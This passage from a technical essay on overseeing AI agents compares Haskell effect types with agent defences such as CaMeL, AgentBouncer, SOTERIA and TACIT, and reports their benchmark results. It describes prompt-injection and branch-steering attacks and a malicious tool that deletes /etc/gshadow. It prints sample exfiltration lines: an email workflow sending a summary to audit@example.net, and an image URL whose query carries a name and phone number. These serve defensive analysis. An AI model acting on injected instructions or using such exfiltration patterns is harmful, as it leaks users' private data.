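Both lists depend on the interpreter, because it *may* skip the second plan but does not always have to. The Stackage documentation for the Haskell library *selective* gives an implementation of `select` that works for every applicative functor and always runs both plans. With it, `payIfCorrect` pays even when the invoice is wrong. The laws require `select` to skip unneeded effects only for types that are also monads, such as `IO`. Mokhov and colleagues wanted this freedom for Haxl, which Facebook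 uses to fetch remote data. Haxl can start fetching for both sides of a condition at once and stop when it has the answer. This is harmless when both sides only read data, but it could make an unwanted payment if one side sends money.

### A fixed sequence with unknown arguments

Neither interface can carry an account number from the invoice to the payment, although the ordinary invoice task always has the same two steps. *Arrows*, an older generalisation of monads, can do this. The type of an arrow names an input as well as an output, and the basic way to join two arrows is to feed the output of one into the other:

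```haskell
(>>>) :: p a b -> p b c -> p a c

payAsAsked = readInvoice "march.pdf" >>> pay
```

`pay` now has the type `p Invoice ()`, which describes a step that waits for an invoice. *Freer Arrows and Why You Need Them in Haskell* (VanDomelen, Kuper and colleagues, 2025) presents a data structure for such plans, with functions that count or list the steps. In its main example, a program fetches text from one web address and posts it to another. An inspector can collect both addresses before the program runs because they are part of the requests, but the text is still unknown.

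In the invoice task, the account is one of the values passed between steps, so an inspector can tell that there will be one payment but not who will receive it. VanDomelen and colleagues also describe an extension with branches. If a loop runs an unknown number of times, an inspector can't analyze the whole program but can still read the loop's body and the parts around it.

| Interface | Invoice task it can express | What an inspector can list at the start |
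|---|---|---|
| Applicative | Read the invoice and pay a preset sum regardless | Read march.pdf, pay 480 to NL-17 |
| Selective | Pay the preset sum only if the invoice matches | Read march.pdf, possibly pay 480 to NL-17 |
| Arrow | Pay whatever the invoice asks for | Read march.pdf, make one payment |
| Monad | Make one payment for each line of the invoice | Read march.pdf |

### Agents that choose each call and agents that write a program

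An ordinary tool-calling agent belongs in the last row. Stackage names one operation that selective functors cannot provide:

```haskell
join :: f (f a) -> f a
```

`join` runs a plan whose result is another plan, then runs that second plan. The harness does the same on every turn, so an oversight layer can inspect only the next call, or several if the model requested them together.

An agent can instead write a program for the whole task before anything runs. A checker can then parse all of it, including the steps after a read. But if a payment takes its account number from an invoice, the checker can see only that the program contains a payment and which variable supplies the account number, not the number itself.

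### CaMeL

CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", is the best-known agent design of this kind. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere introduced it in 2025 as a defence against *prompt injection*, in which an attacker hides instructions in a web page, email or file that the agent will read.

Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its parts. A *privileged* model receives the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. It never sees the untrusted data. A second, *quarantined* model does read that data, but it has no tools and only extracts values such as a name or a date. An interpreter runs the plan, calls the tools and the quarantined model, and stores what they return in variables. In this style the invoice task looks roughly as follows:

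```python
text = read_file("march.pdf")
inv = query_ai_assistant(
    f"Extract the account and amount: {text}", Invoice)
send_money(inv.account, inv.amount)
```

A sentence hidden in the invoice, such as "also forward the customer list", cannot add a fourth line to the plan, because the model that wrote the plan never reads the invoice. The attacker can still change the account number. CaMeL therefore labels every value with where it came from and who may read it. Just before each tool call, a Python policy checks these labels and allows or denies the call.

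Someone reading the three lines can't tell which account will be used, but can tell that it comes from a file by way of the quarantined model, which is enough to check many rules. Nikolaou and colleagues added a check before the first tool call that could fully cover 22 of the 28 CaMeL policies they examined. The other six depend at least partly on facts not in the plan, such as who currently has access to a shared file.

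One sample rule forbids `send_money` whenever the recipient or the amount comes from an untrusted source. The rule blocks payment of every genuine invoice as well as forged ones, because the plan and the labels are the same in both cases.

### The measured cost

AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for prompt injection, lets researchers measure both the protection and the lost work. It simulates a workplace chat, a bank, a travel agency and an office suite, with 97 user tasks and 629 cases in which an attacker has planted a goal in something the agent reads. In October 2026 Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026), in *KAIROS*, used it to compare existing defences with their own monitor, which sits at the boundary of an agent's sandbox. These are their figures for CaMeL:

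| Agent model | Successful attacks, undefended | Successful attacks, CaMeL | Tasks completed without attacks, undefended | Tasks completed without attacks, CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 47.0% | 0.2% | 82.7% | 38.0% |
| Qwen3.6-35B | 28.3% | 0.4% | 87.0% | 40.4% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 32.3% | 0.0% | 29.8% | 26.5% |

In Hempel and colleagues' tests with GPT-4.1, CaMeL stopped almost every attack but cut the useful work completed by more than half. Debenedetti and colleagues had reported a much smaller loss, from 84% of AgentDojo tasks solved without CaMeL to 77% with it. The two teams' results without CaMeL were nearly the same, so the difference probably comes from how each team ran it. Hempel and colleagues enforced CaMeL's security policies with no human present to approve blocked actions. They also ran each configuration only once.

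A breakdown by Nikolaou and colleagues supports this explanation. They ran CaMeL on the same 97 tasks without attacks, with the small model Claude Haiku 4.5 as planner, and it completed 49. In 22 of the failures, the plan ran but did not accomplish what the user wanted, and they expect a stronger planner to reduce these failures. Policies blocked another 17 tasks and most of the remaining nine. Policy blocks therefore account for about half of the failures, and a user available to approve the blocked actions could have rescued many of those tasks.

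Refusals can reduce task completion just as much when an agent plans one step at a time. When Hempel and colleagues made their own monitor refuse every action it could not approve under its policy, task completion fell from 85.1% to 42.7%, close to CaMeL's result, although their agent had fixed no plan in advance. Much of CaMeL's drop from 82.7% to 38.0% therefore comes from refusing to act on untrusted data instead of asking someone, not just from having a readable plan.

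Some tasks rule out a fixed plan. Hempel and colleagues left CaMeL out of their tests on AgentDyn, a set of 60 open-ended tasks in which the agent has to keep planning as it learns more. The clearest example of such a task is "Do what the email from my manager says." The email determines which calls to make, so any plan written before reading it would need `join`.

### Longer plans for using a computer

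*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), which shares two authors with the CaMeL paper, extends CaMeL's design to agents that look at a screen and click. The planner never sees the screen, so it must plan for whatever might be on it. Its plan calls a quarantined vision model to identify what is visible, checks the result against an expectation such as "a cookie banner is showing", and then follows one of the branches written in advance.

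These plans are much longer than the ones for AgentDojo. An average AgentDojo plan has 52 lines, 4.9 tool calls and 3.7 branches. An average computer-use plan has 213 lines, 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, and about half of its steps are fallbacks that a given run never reaches. Foerster and colleagues point out that a user can inspect or approve such a plan before it starts. But the user would have to read 213 lines, and a line that clicks on whatever the vision model finds does not show what the click will do.

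The design was tested on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop applications. Of 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved while watching the screen, the version with a fixed plan solved 31 on the first attempt and 62, or 57%, within five attempts. The five-attempt result assumes that someone can identify the successful attempt.

Foerster and colleagues also tried Fides, a related design in which the planner chooses one action at a time without seeing the tool results. Fides did no better overall. On 60 easier tasks, it solved 33% at the first attempt and 67% within five, compared with 42% and 65% when the planner wrote the whole plan at the start. Fides used almost 30 times as many tokens as an undefended agent, while the single plan used nearly twice as many. Hiding the results from the planner seems to lower the success rate more than making it write the whole plan at the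 start.

An attacker can still influence which branch runs, which Foerster and colleagues call *branch steering*. In one attack, they built an advertisement that looked like a cookie banner. The plan included a sensible step for dismissing cookie banners, so when the vision model found the fake one, the agent clicked it and was taken to the attacker's website. The plan already contained every step the agent took, so a reviewer who had approved every line would have approved the click too.

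### Short programs inside the loop

An agent can also write a few calls, look at the results and then write a few more. Kovalenko and Redchych (2026), in *Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do*, tested this with Qwen3-4B, a small open model they had fine-tuned as an office assistant in a simulated workplace. In one mode, the model makes a single call per turn. In the other, it may write a *tool program*, a group of calls in which a later call can use a field from an earlier result. The program can do nothing else with the results, so it resembles the arrow in the table: its list of calls is fixed before it runs, but some arguments are filled in later.

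On 498 tasks of the kinds it had trained on, the model succeeded in 99.4% with tool programs and 100% with single calls. The programs needed 41% fewer turns with actions, 25% fewer queries to the model and 23% fewer prompt tokens. On a harder set that included unfamiliar kinds of task, the success rate was 81.2% with programs and 80.4% with single calls. In an online shop with entirely new tools, it was 79.0% with programs and 77.9% with single calls. Writing calls ahead therefore hardly reduced success in these tests, but the programs were short. An ideal solution to a task in the first set takes about two calls. The model also sees all results between turns, so it can still change course but has none of CaMeL's protection against injected instructions.

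Capriotti and Kaposi recommend a similar mixture for Haskell programs, in which a monadic plan contains applicative stretches that a program can analyse in full before running them. For an oversight layer, the natural place to end a stretch is just before an action that nobody can undo. Kovalenko and Redchych have such a rule, which allows a call that deletes something, reaches other people or moves money only in a turn after the user has confirmed it.

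The model learned this rule for the office tools, but in the shop it paid, cancelled or refunded without asking 37 times in 547 tasks, up from 7 times before the fine-tuning. The simulated shop recorded these violations but still carried out the calls, so compliance depended on the model, as it did with the instructions that failed to protect PocketOS.

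## Whether the description covers everything the agent does

A rule that payments need confirmation achieves little unless software applies it to every payment, however the agent tries to pay. Security researchers call this requirement *complete mediation*, meaning that every access to a protected object must pass through the component that authorizes it. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026), which credits the principle to Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), adds that mediation is complete only if the agent has no other way to act.

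Railway's 48-hour delay failed this requirement because it did not cover deletions made through the API. Coverage also depends on what is being protected. A perfect checker in Cursor's harness could have stopped this agent, but it could not have stopped another program that held the same token.

### Haskell's back door

Haskell comes close to complete mediation. As Terei, Mazières and colleagues, in *Safe Haskell*, explain, the language does let a program read arbitrary memory and make system calls, but these operations have `IO` types. Code made only of pure functions therefore can't reach them, provided that the type system has no loopholes and that modules can keep their internals private. In ordinary Haskell neither condition holds. The best-known loophole is a single function:

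```haskell
unsafePerformIO :: IO a -> a
```

It performs an action in the middle of a pure computation and hands back the result. GHC's documentation describes it as the "back door" into `IO`. Terei and colleagues give an example that only reads the clock:

```haskell
usec :: IO Integer    -- the time in microseconds

f x = x + unsafePerformIO usec
```

By its type, `f` is an ordinary function on numbers. But `let y = f 3 in y + y` always gives an even number, while `f 3 + f 3` may read the clock twice and give an odd one. A contributor to the forum thread *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?* offers a less innocent example:

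```haskell
freePrize :: Prize
freePrize = unsafePerformIO
  (stealCreditCardDetails >> randomPrize)
```

A reader who checks only the types sees a constant here. `unsafePerformIO` also weakens the free-monad plans of the earlier sections. `simulate` has no `IO` in its type, but it runs the plan's continuations, and a continuation that contains `unsafePerformIO` could send money during the simulation.

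Haskell keeps `unsafePerformIO` because good libraries need it. `ByteString` stores text as packed bytes and handles them with low-level memory operations, but from the outside it behaves like a pure string. According to the documentation, the hidden action should be free of side effects and independent of its environment, but the compiler can't check either condition. In *Using unsafePerformIO safely?*, Haskell programmers discuss whether a program may treat an external logic solver as a pure function. One suggests a version of `unsafePerformIO` that requires a proof of safety, but another suspects that the proof would also have to cover the operating system and the solver.

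### A restricted I/O type

Safe Haskell, part of GHC since version 7.2, closes the known loopholes in code someone else wrote. In a module compiled with the `Safe` flag, GHC rejects `unsafePerformIO`, foreign functions declared with pure types, and Template Haskell, which can access another module's private definitions. The module may import only trusted modules.

None of this restricts `IO` itself. ezyang (2012), in *Unintuitive facts about Safe Haskell*, points out that Safe Haskell accepts a shell command that deletes everything on the disk, because the type `IO ExitCode` openly says that anything may happen. The trusted program must simply never run untrusted code in `IO`. It asks for a narrower type instead:

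```haskell
newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO { runRIO :: IO a }

readAllowed :: FilePath -> RIO String
readAllowed path = UnsafeRIO (
  pathOK path >>= \allowed ->
    if allowed then readFile path else return "")
```

`pathOK` contains the policy, and the functions for reading and writing files both call it. The module exports the type, these two functions and `runRIO`, but not the constructor `UnsafeRIO`. A plugin of type `RIO ()` can chain reads and writes with bind, but it cannot turn its own `IO` actions into `RIO` actions, because `runRIO` only converts `RIO` to `IO`. So every file access by the plugin passes through `pathOK`.

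An `RIO` value still contains a function that no program can read in advance, so the type satisfies the third premise but not the second. A JSON tool call often satisfies the second but not the third.

Safe Haskell still requires some trust. A module that uses unsafe features internally can be labelled `Trustworthy`, meaning its author vouches for it. About two-thirds of the modules in GHC's base library needed that label. According to GHC's *Safe Haskell* guide, whoever compiles the code can decide which packages may contain such modules, but compilation itself can start arbitrary processes. Untrusted code can also use up memory and processor time. Terei and colleagues say they cannot formally guarantee that they have closed every loophole.

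Few programmers adopted Safe Haskell. In the thread on deprecating it, a co-author of the original paper writes that retiring it would be plausible. In *Safe Haskell?*, Eisenberg (2021) says he started drafting a proposal to remove it but changed his mind, and argues that it needs renovation as part of a larger security overhaul. SPISE MISU's *Agent.IO.Restricted* (2026), an experimental Haskell package, has since applied the idea to agents. It gives a language-model agent an `RIO` type with separate permissions for reading code, saving it and posting. The next section discusses this use of capability types.

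### Scripts, tests and other agents

When a coding agent asks to run a project's tests, the request is readable and sensible, but executing it runs whatever code the repository contains. The request looks the same even if an attacker has added malicious code to the tests. Any tool that executes code is like `unsafePerformIO` in this respect, since its type or JSON schema doesn't limit what that code does.

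Developers can at least route all the tools they know about through one checkpoint. *Metis* (2026), a system for coding agents, uses a single registry to look up built-in tools, plugins and tools from outside servers before dispatching them. Each shell step in a workflow needs the same permission as an ordinary shell command. This keeps workflows from bypassing the shell's permission check, but it doesn't make shell scripts easier to read.

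Delegation leaves another gap in the description. If a coding agent runs a command that starts a second agent, the first agent's harness records one shell command, but the second agent may have other tools, looser permission settings and no human reviewer. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* addresses this by defining the agent to include every process that runs for it, including the model, the code that drives it and anything they start. An oversight layer that adopts this definition has to confine all of these processes. Even this confinement doesn't cover an agent on another company's server that receives its instructions by email.

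Coverage is easy to overestimate. In *Governed MCP*, Son (2026) put a checkpoint for tool calls into the kernel, the core of the operating system, where an agent can't switch it off. In the first version of the paper, Son claimed that the checkpoint covered all 123 paths from agent to system. A rebuilt test found only 59 paths. Of these, 43 went through the checkpoint, ten only read data or touched nothing that the policy governs, and six reached real resources without any check. Son withdrew the claim and disclosed the gap.

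### Reading as an effect

The description should include reads, even though a read seems to leave the world unchanged. Haskell gives reading the clock an `IO` type, although looking at the time doesn't change it. The reason to include reads is stronger for agents, because a request for information is itself a message to whoever answers it.

Suppose an agent has read a customer list and then fetches this address:

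```
https://example.com/logo.png?id=Maria+Lopez+0612345678
```

A request typed as reading a picture can still send the server a name and a telephone number, which the server may log even if it has no such picture. A search query can carry data out in the same way. The bibliography program of Zhou and colleagues is allowed to search a database of papers, and the type of a search string doesn't limit it to paper titles. A policy that checks writes but allows all reads therefore leaves a way for data to get out.

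*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) describes the usual compromise for coding agents, in which the agent may read the passwords and keys on its machine, but these must never reach an untrusted server. The system also checks network requests by routing them through a proxy. A list of approved websites isn't enough, because the paper assumes that an attacker may also control content on legitimate services.

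Even then, information still leaves the agent in two ways. Each query to the model sends the conversation to the company that hosts it, and Joos and Pradel have to assume that this company doesn't misuse the data. The agent's final answer also goes to a person and may influence them, a problem discussed in the section on reviewers.

### One command seen from two places

An oversight layer can check an agent's tool calls, or it can check the resulting programs' *system calls*, which are requests to the operating system, for example to open a file, delete it or start a process. In Joos and Pradel's main example, the same event looks very different at these two levels. An attacker supplies a tool named `validate_patch`, described as confirming that a code change applies cleanly. The tool does this, then silently deletes `/etc/gshadow`, the file with the system's group passwords.

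| | At the tool call | At the system call |
|---|---|---|
| What the checker receives | `validate_patch(path)` | Delete `/etc/gshadow` |
| What is clear | The purpose, as the tool's description gives it | The operation and the file |
| What is missing | Anything the tool's code does beyond its description | The user's task, and whether it calls for a deletion |

Defences that read only the conversation and the tool calls had no evidence of the attack. Two of them allowed the call. A third avoided the attack only because it refused 31 of 39 harmless calls, so the agent never reached the malicious tool. Another defence monitored events inside the system. It correctly flagged the deletion and killed the process, but the file was already gone.

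AgentBouncer intercepts the system call before the kernel executes it. The request in this example is suspicious on its own, but most requests are hard to judge without context. Deleting a cache file, for instance, can be routine in one task and sabotage in another. AgentBouncer therefore passes down the user's task, the tool's description and the model's stated reason for calling the tool from the upper level. A second language model then judges whether the operation is safe and necessary for the task. Fixed rules and stored decisions settle most requests, so this model judges only the rest. A refused operation fails with a permission error, but the rest of the tool can keep running. With `validate_patch`, the file survived and the agent still finished its task.

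Joos and Pradel tested AgentBouncer on 340 attacks, which combined 85 goals with four attack methods: injected instructions, malicious tools, scripts already on the machine, and tests in the repository. Without protection, 338 attacks succeeded; with AgentBouncer, 36 did. The agent solved about as many ordinary tasks with AgentBouncer as without it (72.9% and 71.5%). Intercepting a system call does not guarantee a correct verdict on it, because a language model still makes that judgment, and part of what it reads, including the tool's description, may come from the attacker.

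Hempel and colleagues' sandbox monitor has the same trade-off. It covers every channel, but it can only approximate where data came from and can't determine in advance what the user intends.

Neither level covers anything outside the machine, such as what Railway did with the PocketOS agent's web request or the tools that Anthropic runs on its own servers.

### Proofs about the executor

Two lines of work in 2026 prove properties of the software that carries out a language model's requests. That software is ordinary code, but nobody can yet prove much about what the model will request.

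McCann's Rocq proof uses a permission flag to show that a governed workflow does no input or output without a preceding check. The flag starts as false, a passed check sets it to true, and the definition of a safe execution allows I/O events only while it is true. The definition in *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* resets the flag after each event, but the code in McCann's first paper leaves it true, so one passed check can cover several events.

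The wrapper runs its checks before every request, but a single request can do a lot. McCann's model has 14 kinds of request, including web requests, memory operations, queries to a language model and running a command. A command that rewrites a thousand files counts as one request, so one round of checks satisfies the theorem.

*Algebraic Semantics* also proves that every program expressible in the model is governed, and that ungoverned I/O can't be expressed in it. This resembles the argument for Haskell and has the same weak point. The model treats ordinary computation between requests as pure, but in the running system, a module that opened a file directly would perform an effect inside supposedly pure code, as `unsafePerformIO` does in Haskell. The safety theorems assume that no module does this. McCann leaves enforcement to a companion paper, whose system compiles modules to WebAssembly,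 a format that can run in a sandbox, and certifies their purity.

The *trusted base* of a proof is everything that must be correct for the result to hold in practice. McCann's contains Rocq's own proof checker, the library of interaction trees and the system that runs the workflows. Rocq translates part of the proved code into OCaml, but the C code that connects this to the rest of the system is unverified. If the translated component is unavailable, an implementation in another language, Elixir, takes over. Random testing checks the versions against each other, and in the first campaign the 188th input exposed a bug in the handling of permissions. The proof that nobody can alter the log unnoticed also assumes a hash function that never gives two inputs the same value, which no practical hash function can guarantee.

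In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) use the verification language Dafny to verify PocketFlow, a very small framework for building agents. They represent the model as a procedure with no body that may return any value of type `Action`. Dafny must then prove that the framework follows its policy for every such value. Under the policy, the agent may read files only inside its workspace, call only tools on a list, and take no more than a fixed number of steps. Because the proof covers every possible action, it doesn't depend on the model's training or capability.

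The proof depends on what Moon and Varshney call *effect exclusivity*, the assumption that the agent has no external effects except through the `Action` interface. This is complete mediation again, so the third premise is an assumption of the proof, not a result. The trusted base also includes the policy itself, the correspondence between the modelled events and real ones, the code that turns the model's text into an `Action`, and Dafny's verifier and compiler.

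If `validate_patch` were on the list of permitted tools, the agent's call would comply with the verified policy and the password file would still disappear. Moon and Varshney accept this limit. They write that a general shell command "collapses the guarantee onto the primitive" and recommend a sandbox underneath. PocketFlow's interface has only four kinds of action, far fewer than a typical coding agent needs.

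A proof can also succeed because the safety rule it proves applies to nothing. Moon and Varshney had language models write the specifications and proofs, starting from a template of safety properties. For one agent, which retrieves documents, the template had no field that matched the agent's real effects. When the model writing the specification had access to the agent's code, it left the nearest field empty. The safety rule then applied to an empty list and was trivially true. Dafny accepted the proof, and the specification passed three automatic tests meant to catch poor specifications. Moon and Varshney want to add a test that each safety rule has something to apply to in a state the agent can reach.

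## Checking a described plan by program analysis, types and proof

The fourth premise is that a reviewer can tell acceptable proposals from unacceptable ones. The reviewer can be a program, which doesn't get tired and gives the same plan the same verdict every time. But someone first has to define "acceptable" in terms a program can compute.

### Following data through an e-mail workflow

Meijer's article *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), which preceded his talk, describes an assistant with one tool for fetching mail and another for sending it. A user, Michelle, asks it to summarize her inbox. One message, disguised as a compliance notice, contains instructions to send a summary to an outside address and not to mention it. An agent that chooses one tool call at a time may obey, and Michelle then gets a summary that omits that message.

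Meijer has the model write the whole workflow before fetching anything, as CaMeL does, so a message can't add a step. But an attacker can also put the instruction into the description of the mail tool, which the model reads while planning, and a malicious user can simply ask for the extra step. The model may then write the following workflow, shown here in Python instead of Meijer's JSON:

```python
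emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize(emails)
send_email(to="audit@example.net", body=summary)
return summary
```

Meijer's rule against this specifies a *source*, the result of fetching mail, and a *sink*, the body of a message to an address outside the company. A data-flow analysis marks whatever comes from the source and follows the mark through the program. It marks `emails` on line 1, then `summary` on line 2, because `summary` is computed from a marked value. On line 3 a marked value reaches the body of a message to an address outside the company's domain, so the checker rejects the workflow before any mail is fetched. Meijer suggests using CodeQL or Semgrep, which programmers already use to analyse ordinary code.

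The analysis doesn't depend on what the messages say, so no wording can get past it. For the same reason, it can't detect whether a summary reveals anything sensitive. "You have four new messages" carries the same mark as a full copy of the inbox. The rule also blocks a summary that Michelle wants to send to her lawyer, unless someone has listed the lawyer's domain. If the workflow takes the address from a variable, the checker must either treat the address as unlisted or leave it to be checked at run time.

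### Deleting two files

A data-flow rule restricts where values go, but checking what a workflow accomplishes requires a *specification*. This includes *preconditions*, which must be true before an operation runs, and *postconditions*, which will be true afterwards. A verifier such as Dafny tries to prove that the postcondition of the whole workflow follows from the postconditions of its steps.

In Meijer's example, a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The deletion tool accepts patterns, and the model notices that one call with `*.txt`, which matches every text file, makes a shorter workflow than two separate calls. An obvious specification is:

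```
delete_file(pattern)
  ensures: every file matching pattern is absent

task
  ensures: foo.txt is absent and bar.txt is absent
```

The call with `*.txt` satisfies this specification because both names match the pattern, so both files are absent afterwards. The proof is correct even though the call also deletes the user's other text files.

The same specification even rejects the sensible workflow, which deletes `foo.txt` and then `bar.txt`. The tool's postcondition guarantees only that `bar.txt` is absent after the second call, so it doesn't rule out that deleting `bar.txt` brought `foo.txt` back.

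Both faults have the same remedy, a *frame condition*, which states what an operation leaves unchanged. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described the underlying difficulty, the *frame problem*, in 1969. Meijer writes out a frame condition for the tool, but the task needs one too:

```
delete_file(pattern)
  ensures: every file matching pattern is absent
  ensures: every other file exists if and only if it did before

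task
  ensures: foo.txt is absent and bar.txt is absent
  ensures: every other file exists if and only if it did before
```

Now the call with `*.txt` fails verification, because it would remove a file such as `notes.txt`, which the task's frame condition protects. The two separate calls pass, because the tool's frame condition guarantees that each call affects only the file it names.

This specification still covers only whether files exist, so it would accept a workflow that empties `notes.txt`, as happened to Meijer's source file.

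### Proof-carrying code

In Meijer's design, the agent has to supply a proof along with its plan. The idea comes from Necula and Lee's 1996 operating systems paper, *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*. A kernel sometimes has to run code supplied by an ordinary program, such as a filter that picks out the network packets the program wants, but bad code running inside the kernel could overwrite anything. Necula and Lee's kernel therefore publishes a safety policy, and the program supplies its machine code with a formal proof that the code obeys the policy. Once the kernel has validated the proof, it can run the code without further checks. Necula and Lee called this *proof-carrying code*.

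The method works because checking a proof is much easier than finding one. The kernel's check doesn't depend on who wrote the code or whether the software that found the proof is reliable, since a faulty proof fails validation. A digital signature identifies the author but doesn't show what the code does. The method suits language models because an unreliable model can write the proof, and if it makes a mistake, it only has to try again. Meijer presents his scheme as an extension of the way Java and .NET verify compiled code before running it.

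The analogy is weaker for the policy. Every packet filter has to stay within its own memory, so one policy can cover them all. A request to delete two files needs its own postcondition and frame condition, and someone has to derive them from an English sentence. Proof-carrying code removes the need to trust whoever wrote the plan, but the policy still has to be correct.

### Proving a plan for an airline agent

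A company can spread this work by writing one specification for a whole kind of business. He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *SOTERIA*, did this for customer-service agents. They turned an airline's policy document into 24 formulas. One of them says that the agent may cancel a reservation only after checking that the passenger hasn't flown any part of it:

```
for every call  Cancel(r)
there is an earlier call  CheckNotFlown(r)  that returned true
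```

A language model writes a plan in a small language of states and transitions. Each transition makes at most one tool call, and conditions determine which branch runs. Dafny then checks that every call meets the tool's precondition, that the plan can't get stuck, and that every path obeys every formula. Suppose a plan looks up a booking, computes its age and cancels it if it is less than 24 hours old. The verifier treats the age as an unknown number and examines both branches. It finds a path that cancels the booking without checking whether the flight has already been flown, so it rejects the plan before the agent calls any tool. The planner receives an error message and can retry up to eight times.

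He and colleagues tested SOTERIA on 207 tasks from three benchmarks with four models, and no run violated the specifications. The design ensures this, because a monitor also checks every call against the same formulas and blocks any violation. Task completion is a better measure of the system's usefulness. On the airline tasks, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 88% without a violation using SOTERIA, compared with 56% using the best competing guard, but SOTERIA raised the cost per task from 32 cents with no guard to 80 cents. On Toolathlon, which has long tasks with files and documents, the model completed 18.6% with SOTERIA. With no guard it completed 30.2%, but only 11.6% without breaking a rule.

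Another experiment on the airline tasks added the parts of SOTERIA one at a time:

| Configuration | Violations, GPT-5.4-mini | Violations, Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 13 | 27 |
| Verification added | 10 | 24 |
| Library of verified sub-plans added | 12 | 22 |
| Run-time monitor added | 0 | 0 |

Verifying the plans removed few violations. Some plans ran without complete proofs, but 65 of 68 plans, including sub-plans, passed verification in a test with GPT-5.4-mini, so unproved plans probably explain few of the remaining violations. The executor is probably the larger cause. A Haskell interpreter carries out the plan it receives, whereas SOTERIA normally shows the plan to a second language model, which may choose other calls, so the proof applies to a plan that the agent need not follow. SOTERIA also has a strict mode that permits only the transitions in the plan.

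### Types that track authority

Type checkers prove simpler properties, but do so automatically. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system from the Swiss university EPFL in which agents act by writing Scala 3 programs. The compiler checks each program before it runs.

A *capability* here is a program value that grants access to a resource, such as an open file. Code that doesn't hold the value can't use the file. Scala's checker records in a function's type which capabilities the function holds, and this record is called a *capture set*:

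```scala
val f = fs.access("OUTPUT.md")

(s: String) => s.toUpperCase   // String -> String
(s: String) => f.write(s)      // String ->{f} Unit
```

The plain arrow stands for a pure function, and `->{f}` for one that may use `f`. Haskell would give the second function the type `String -> IO ()`, the same type it would give a function that writes to another file or sends the text over a network.

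TACIT uses pure functions to protect secrets. Reading a confidential file returns its contents in a wrapper:

```scala
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]

val key = readClassified("key.txt")

key.map(s => s.length)                   // accepted
key.map(s => { f.write(s); s.length })   // rejected
```

`map` applies a function to the secret and wraps the result again. Because `map` accepts only pure functions, an agent's program can compute with the key but can't write it to a file or send it anywhere. The agent also lacks the capability needed to unwrap the key. If the program prints the key, the user's terminal shows it, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. TACIT's compiler rejects code that would leak the key before it runs, whereas CaMeL attaches its labels to data while a plan runs.

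Some tasks, such as summarizing a confidential contract, require a language model to read the secret. For these, the program can pass the wrapped text to a second model on the user's own machine and get a wrapped answer back. The trusted components are the compiler, the runtime, the library that defines the capabilities and this local model. Odersky and colleagues treat the cloud model that writes the programs as a possible attacker. Its code must compile in a *safe mode* that forbids type casts and reflection, which could hide a capability much as `unsafePerformIO` hides an effect.

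To test TACIT, they gave agents a software project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with ten injected attacks and added 11 requests that asked for the secrets directly or under a pretext. These are the trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

| Trials | Protection | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 120 with injected attacks | Wrapper | 120 | 120 |
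| 120 with injected attacks | None | 120 | 117 |
| 11 malicious requests | Wrapper | 11 | 11 |
| 11 malicious requests | None | 9 | 3 |

Sonnet resisted every injected attack without the wrapper, so the types gave it no added protection against these attacks. They made a large difference for MiniMax, which leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious requests when the files were plain text. With the wrapper, Sonnet still completed 99.2% of its tasks and MiniMax 90.0%. On AgentDojo's standard tasks, TACIT blocked all but one of the injections.

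These agents lost little performance by writing typed programs. On the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real programming problems, MiniMax's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7% with TACIT.

TACIT leaves some channels open. A program could leak one bit of a secret by taking longer when that bit is 1. An external command runs outside the type system, so the only protection is a list of permitted commands. Types also can't narrow a broad permission. TACIT's network permission is a list of hosts, so a program that may contact Railway could send `volumeDelete` as easily as a request to add a domain. To prevent this, the library's author would have to provide a separate function for each operation.

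*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu et al., 2026) extends TACIT to programs that are already running. When execution reaches a call such as `agent[Int]("subtract 50 and return the new balance")`, a model writes the missing code, and the compiler checks it in the context of the surrounding code. In one example, the generated code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the whole fragment before any of it runs, so the balance stays at 100. In Python, the subtraction would have run before the error appeared. A fragment that passes the check can still fail halfway if a server refuses the second of two requests.

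The compiler rejected 8.6% of generated fragments on a search benchmark and 22.4% on τ²-bench's retail tasks. Zhao and colleagues call LACUNA's overall τ²-bench result on par with ordinary tool calling, but in their table DeepSeek's model solved 76.0% of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% without it. The favourable figures for TACIT therefore don't hold for every way of writing typed agent code.

### Checking the order of requests

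Capture sets record what a program may use, but not in what order, so they can't express a policy that a human must approve a patch before the agent writes it. Tan and colleagues' language ETAS checks such ordering rules, even when a dry-run handler intercepts the write.

An ordinary effect type drops the write once the handler answers it, but ETAS's second record, the *request summary*, keeps it. A handler can extend this summary but never shorten it. With *g* for a request for approval and *w* for a write, the patch program has these two records:

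| | Effects left for the caller | Request summary |
|---|---|---|
| Real run | g, w | g, then possibly w |
| Dry run | g | g, then possibly w |

The summary is a regular expression, a pattern that describes a set of sequences. The approval rule is another:

```
summary:  g w?
rule:     (g (g|w)*)?
```

The rule allows either no requests or a *g* followed by any mixture of *g* and *w*. The compiler turns it into a small state machine that starts in the state "not approved". A *g* moves it to "approved", where it stays. A *w* that arrives before any *g* moves it to "violated". The compiler then runs every sequence in the summary through the machine. If none reaches "violated", the program needs no further check of this rule. If all do, the compiler rejects the program.

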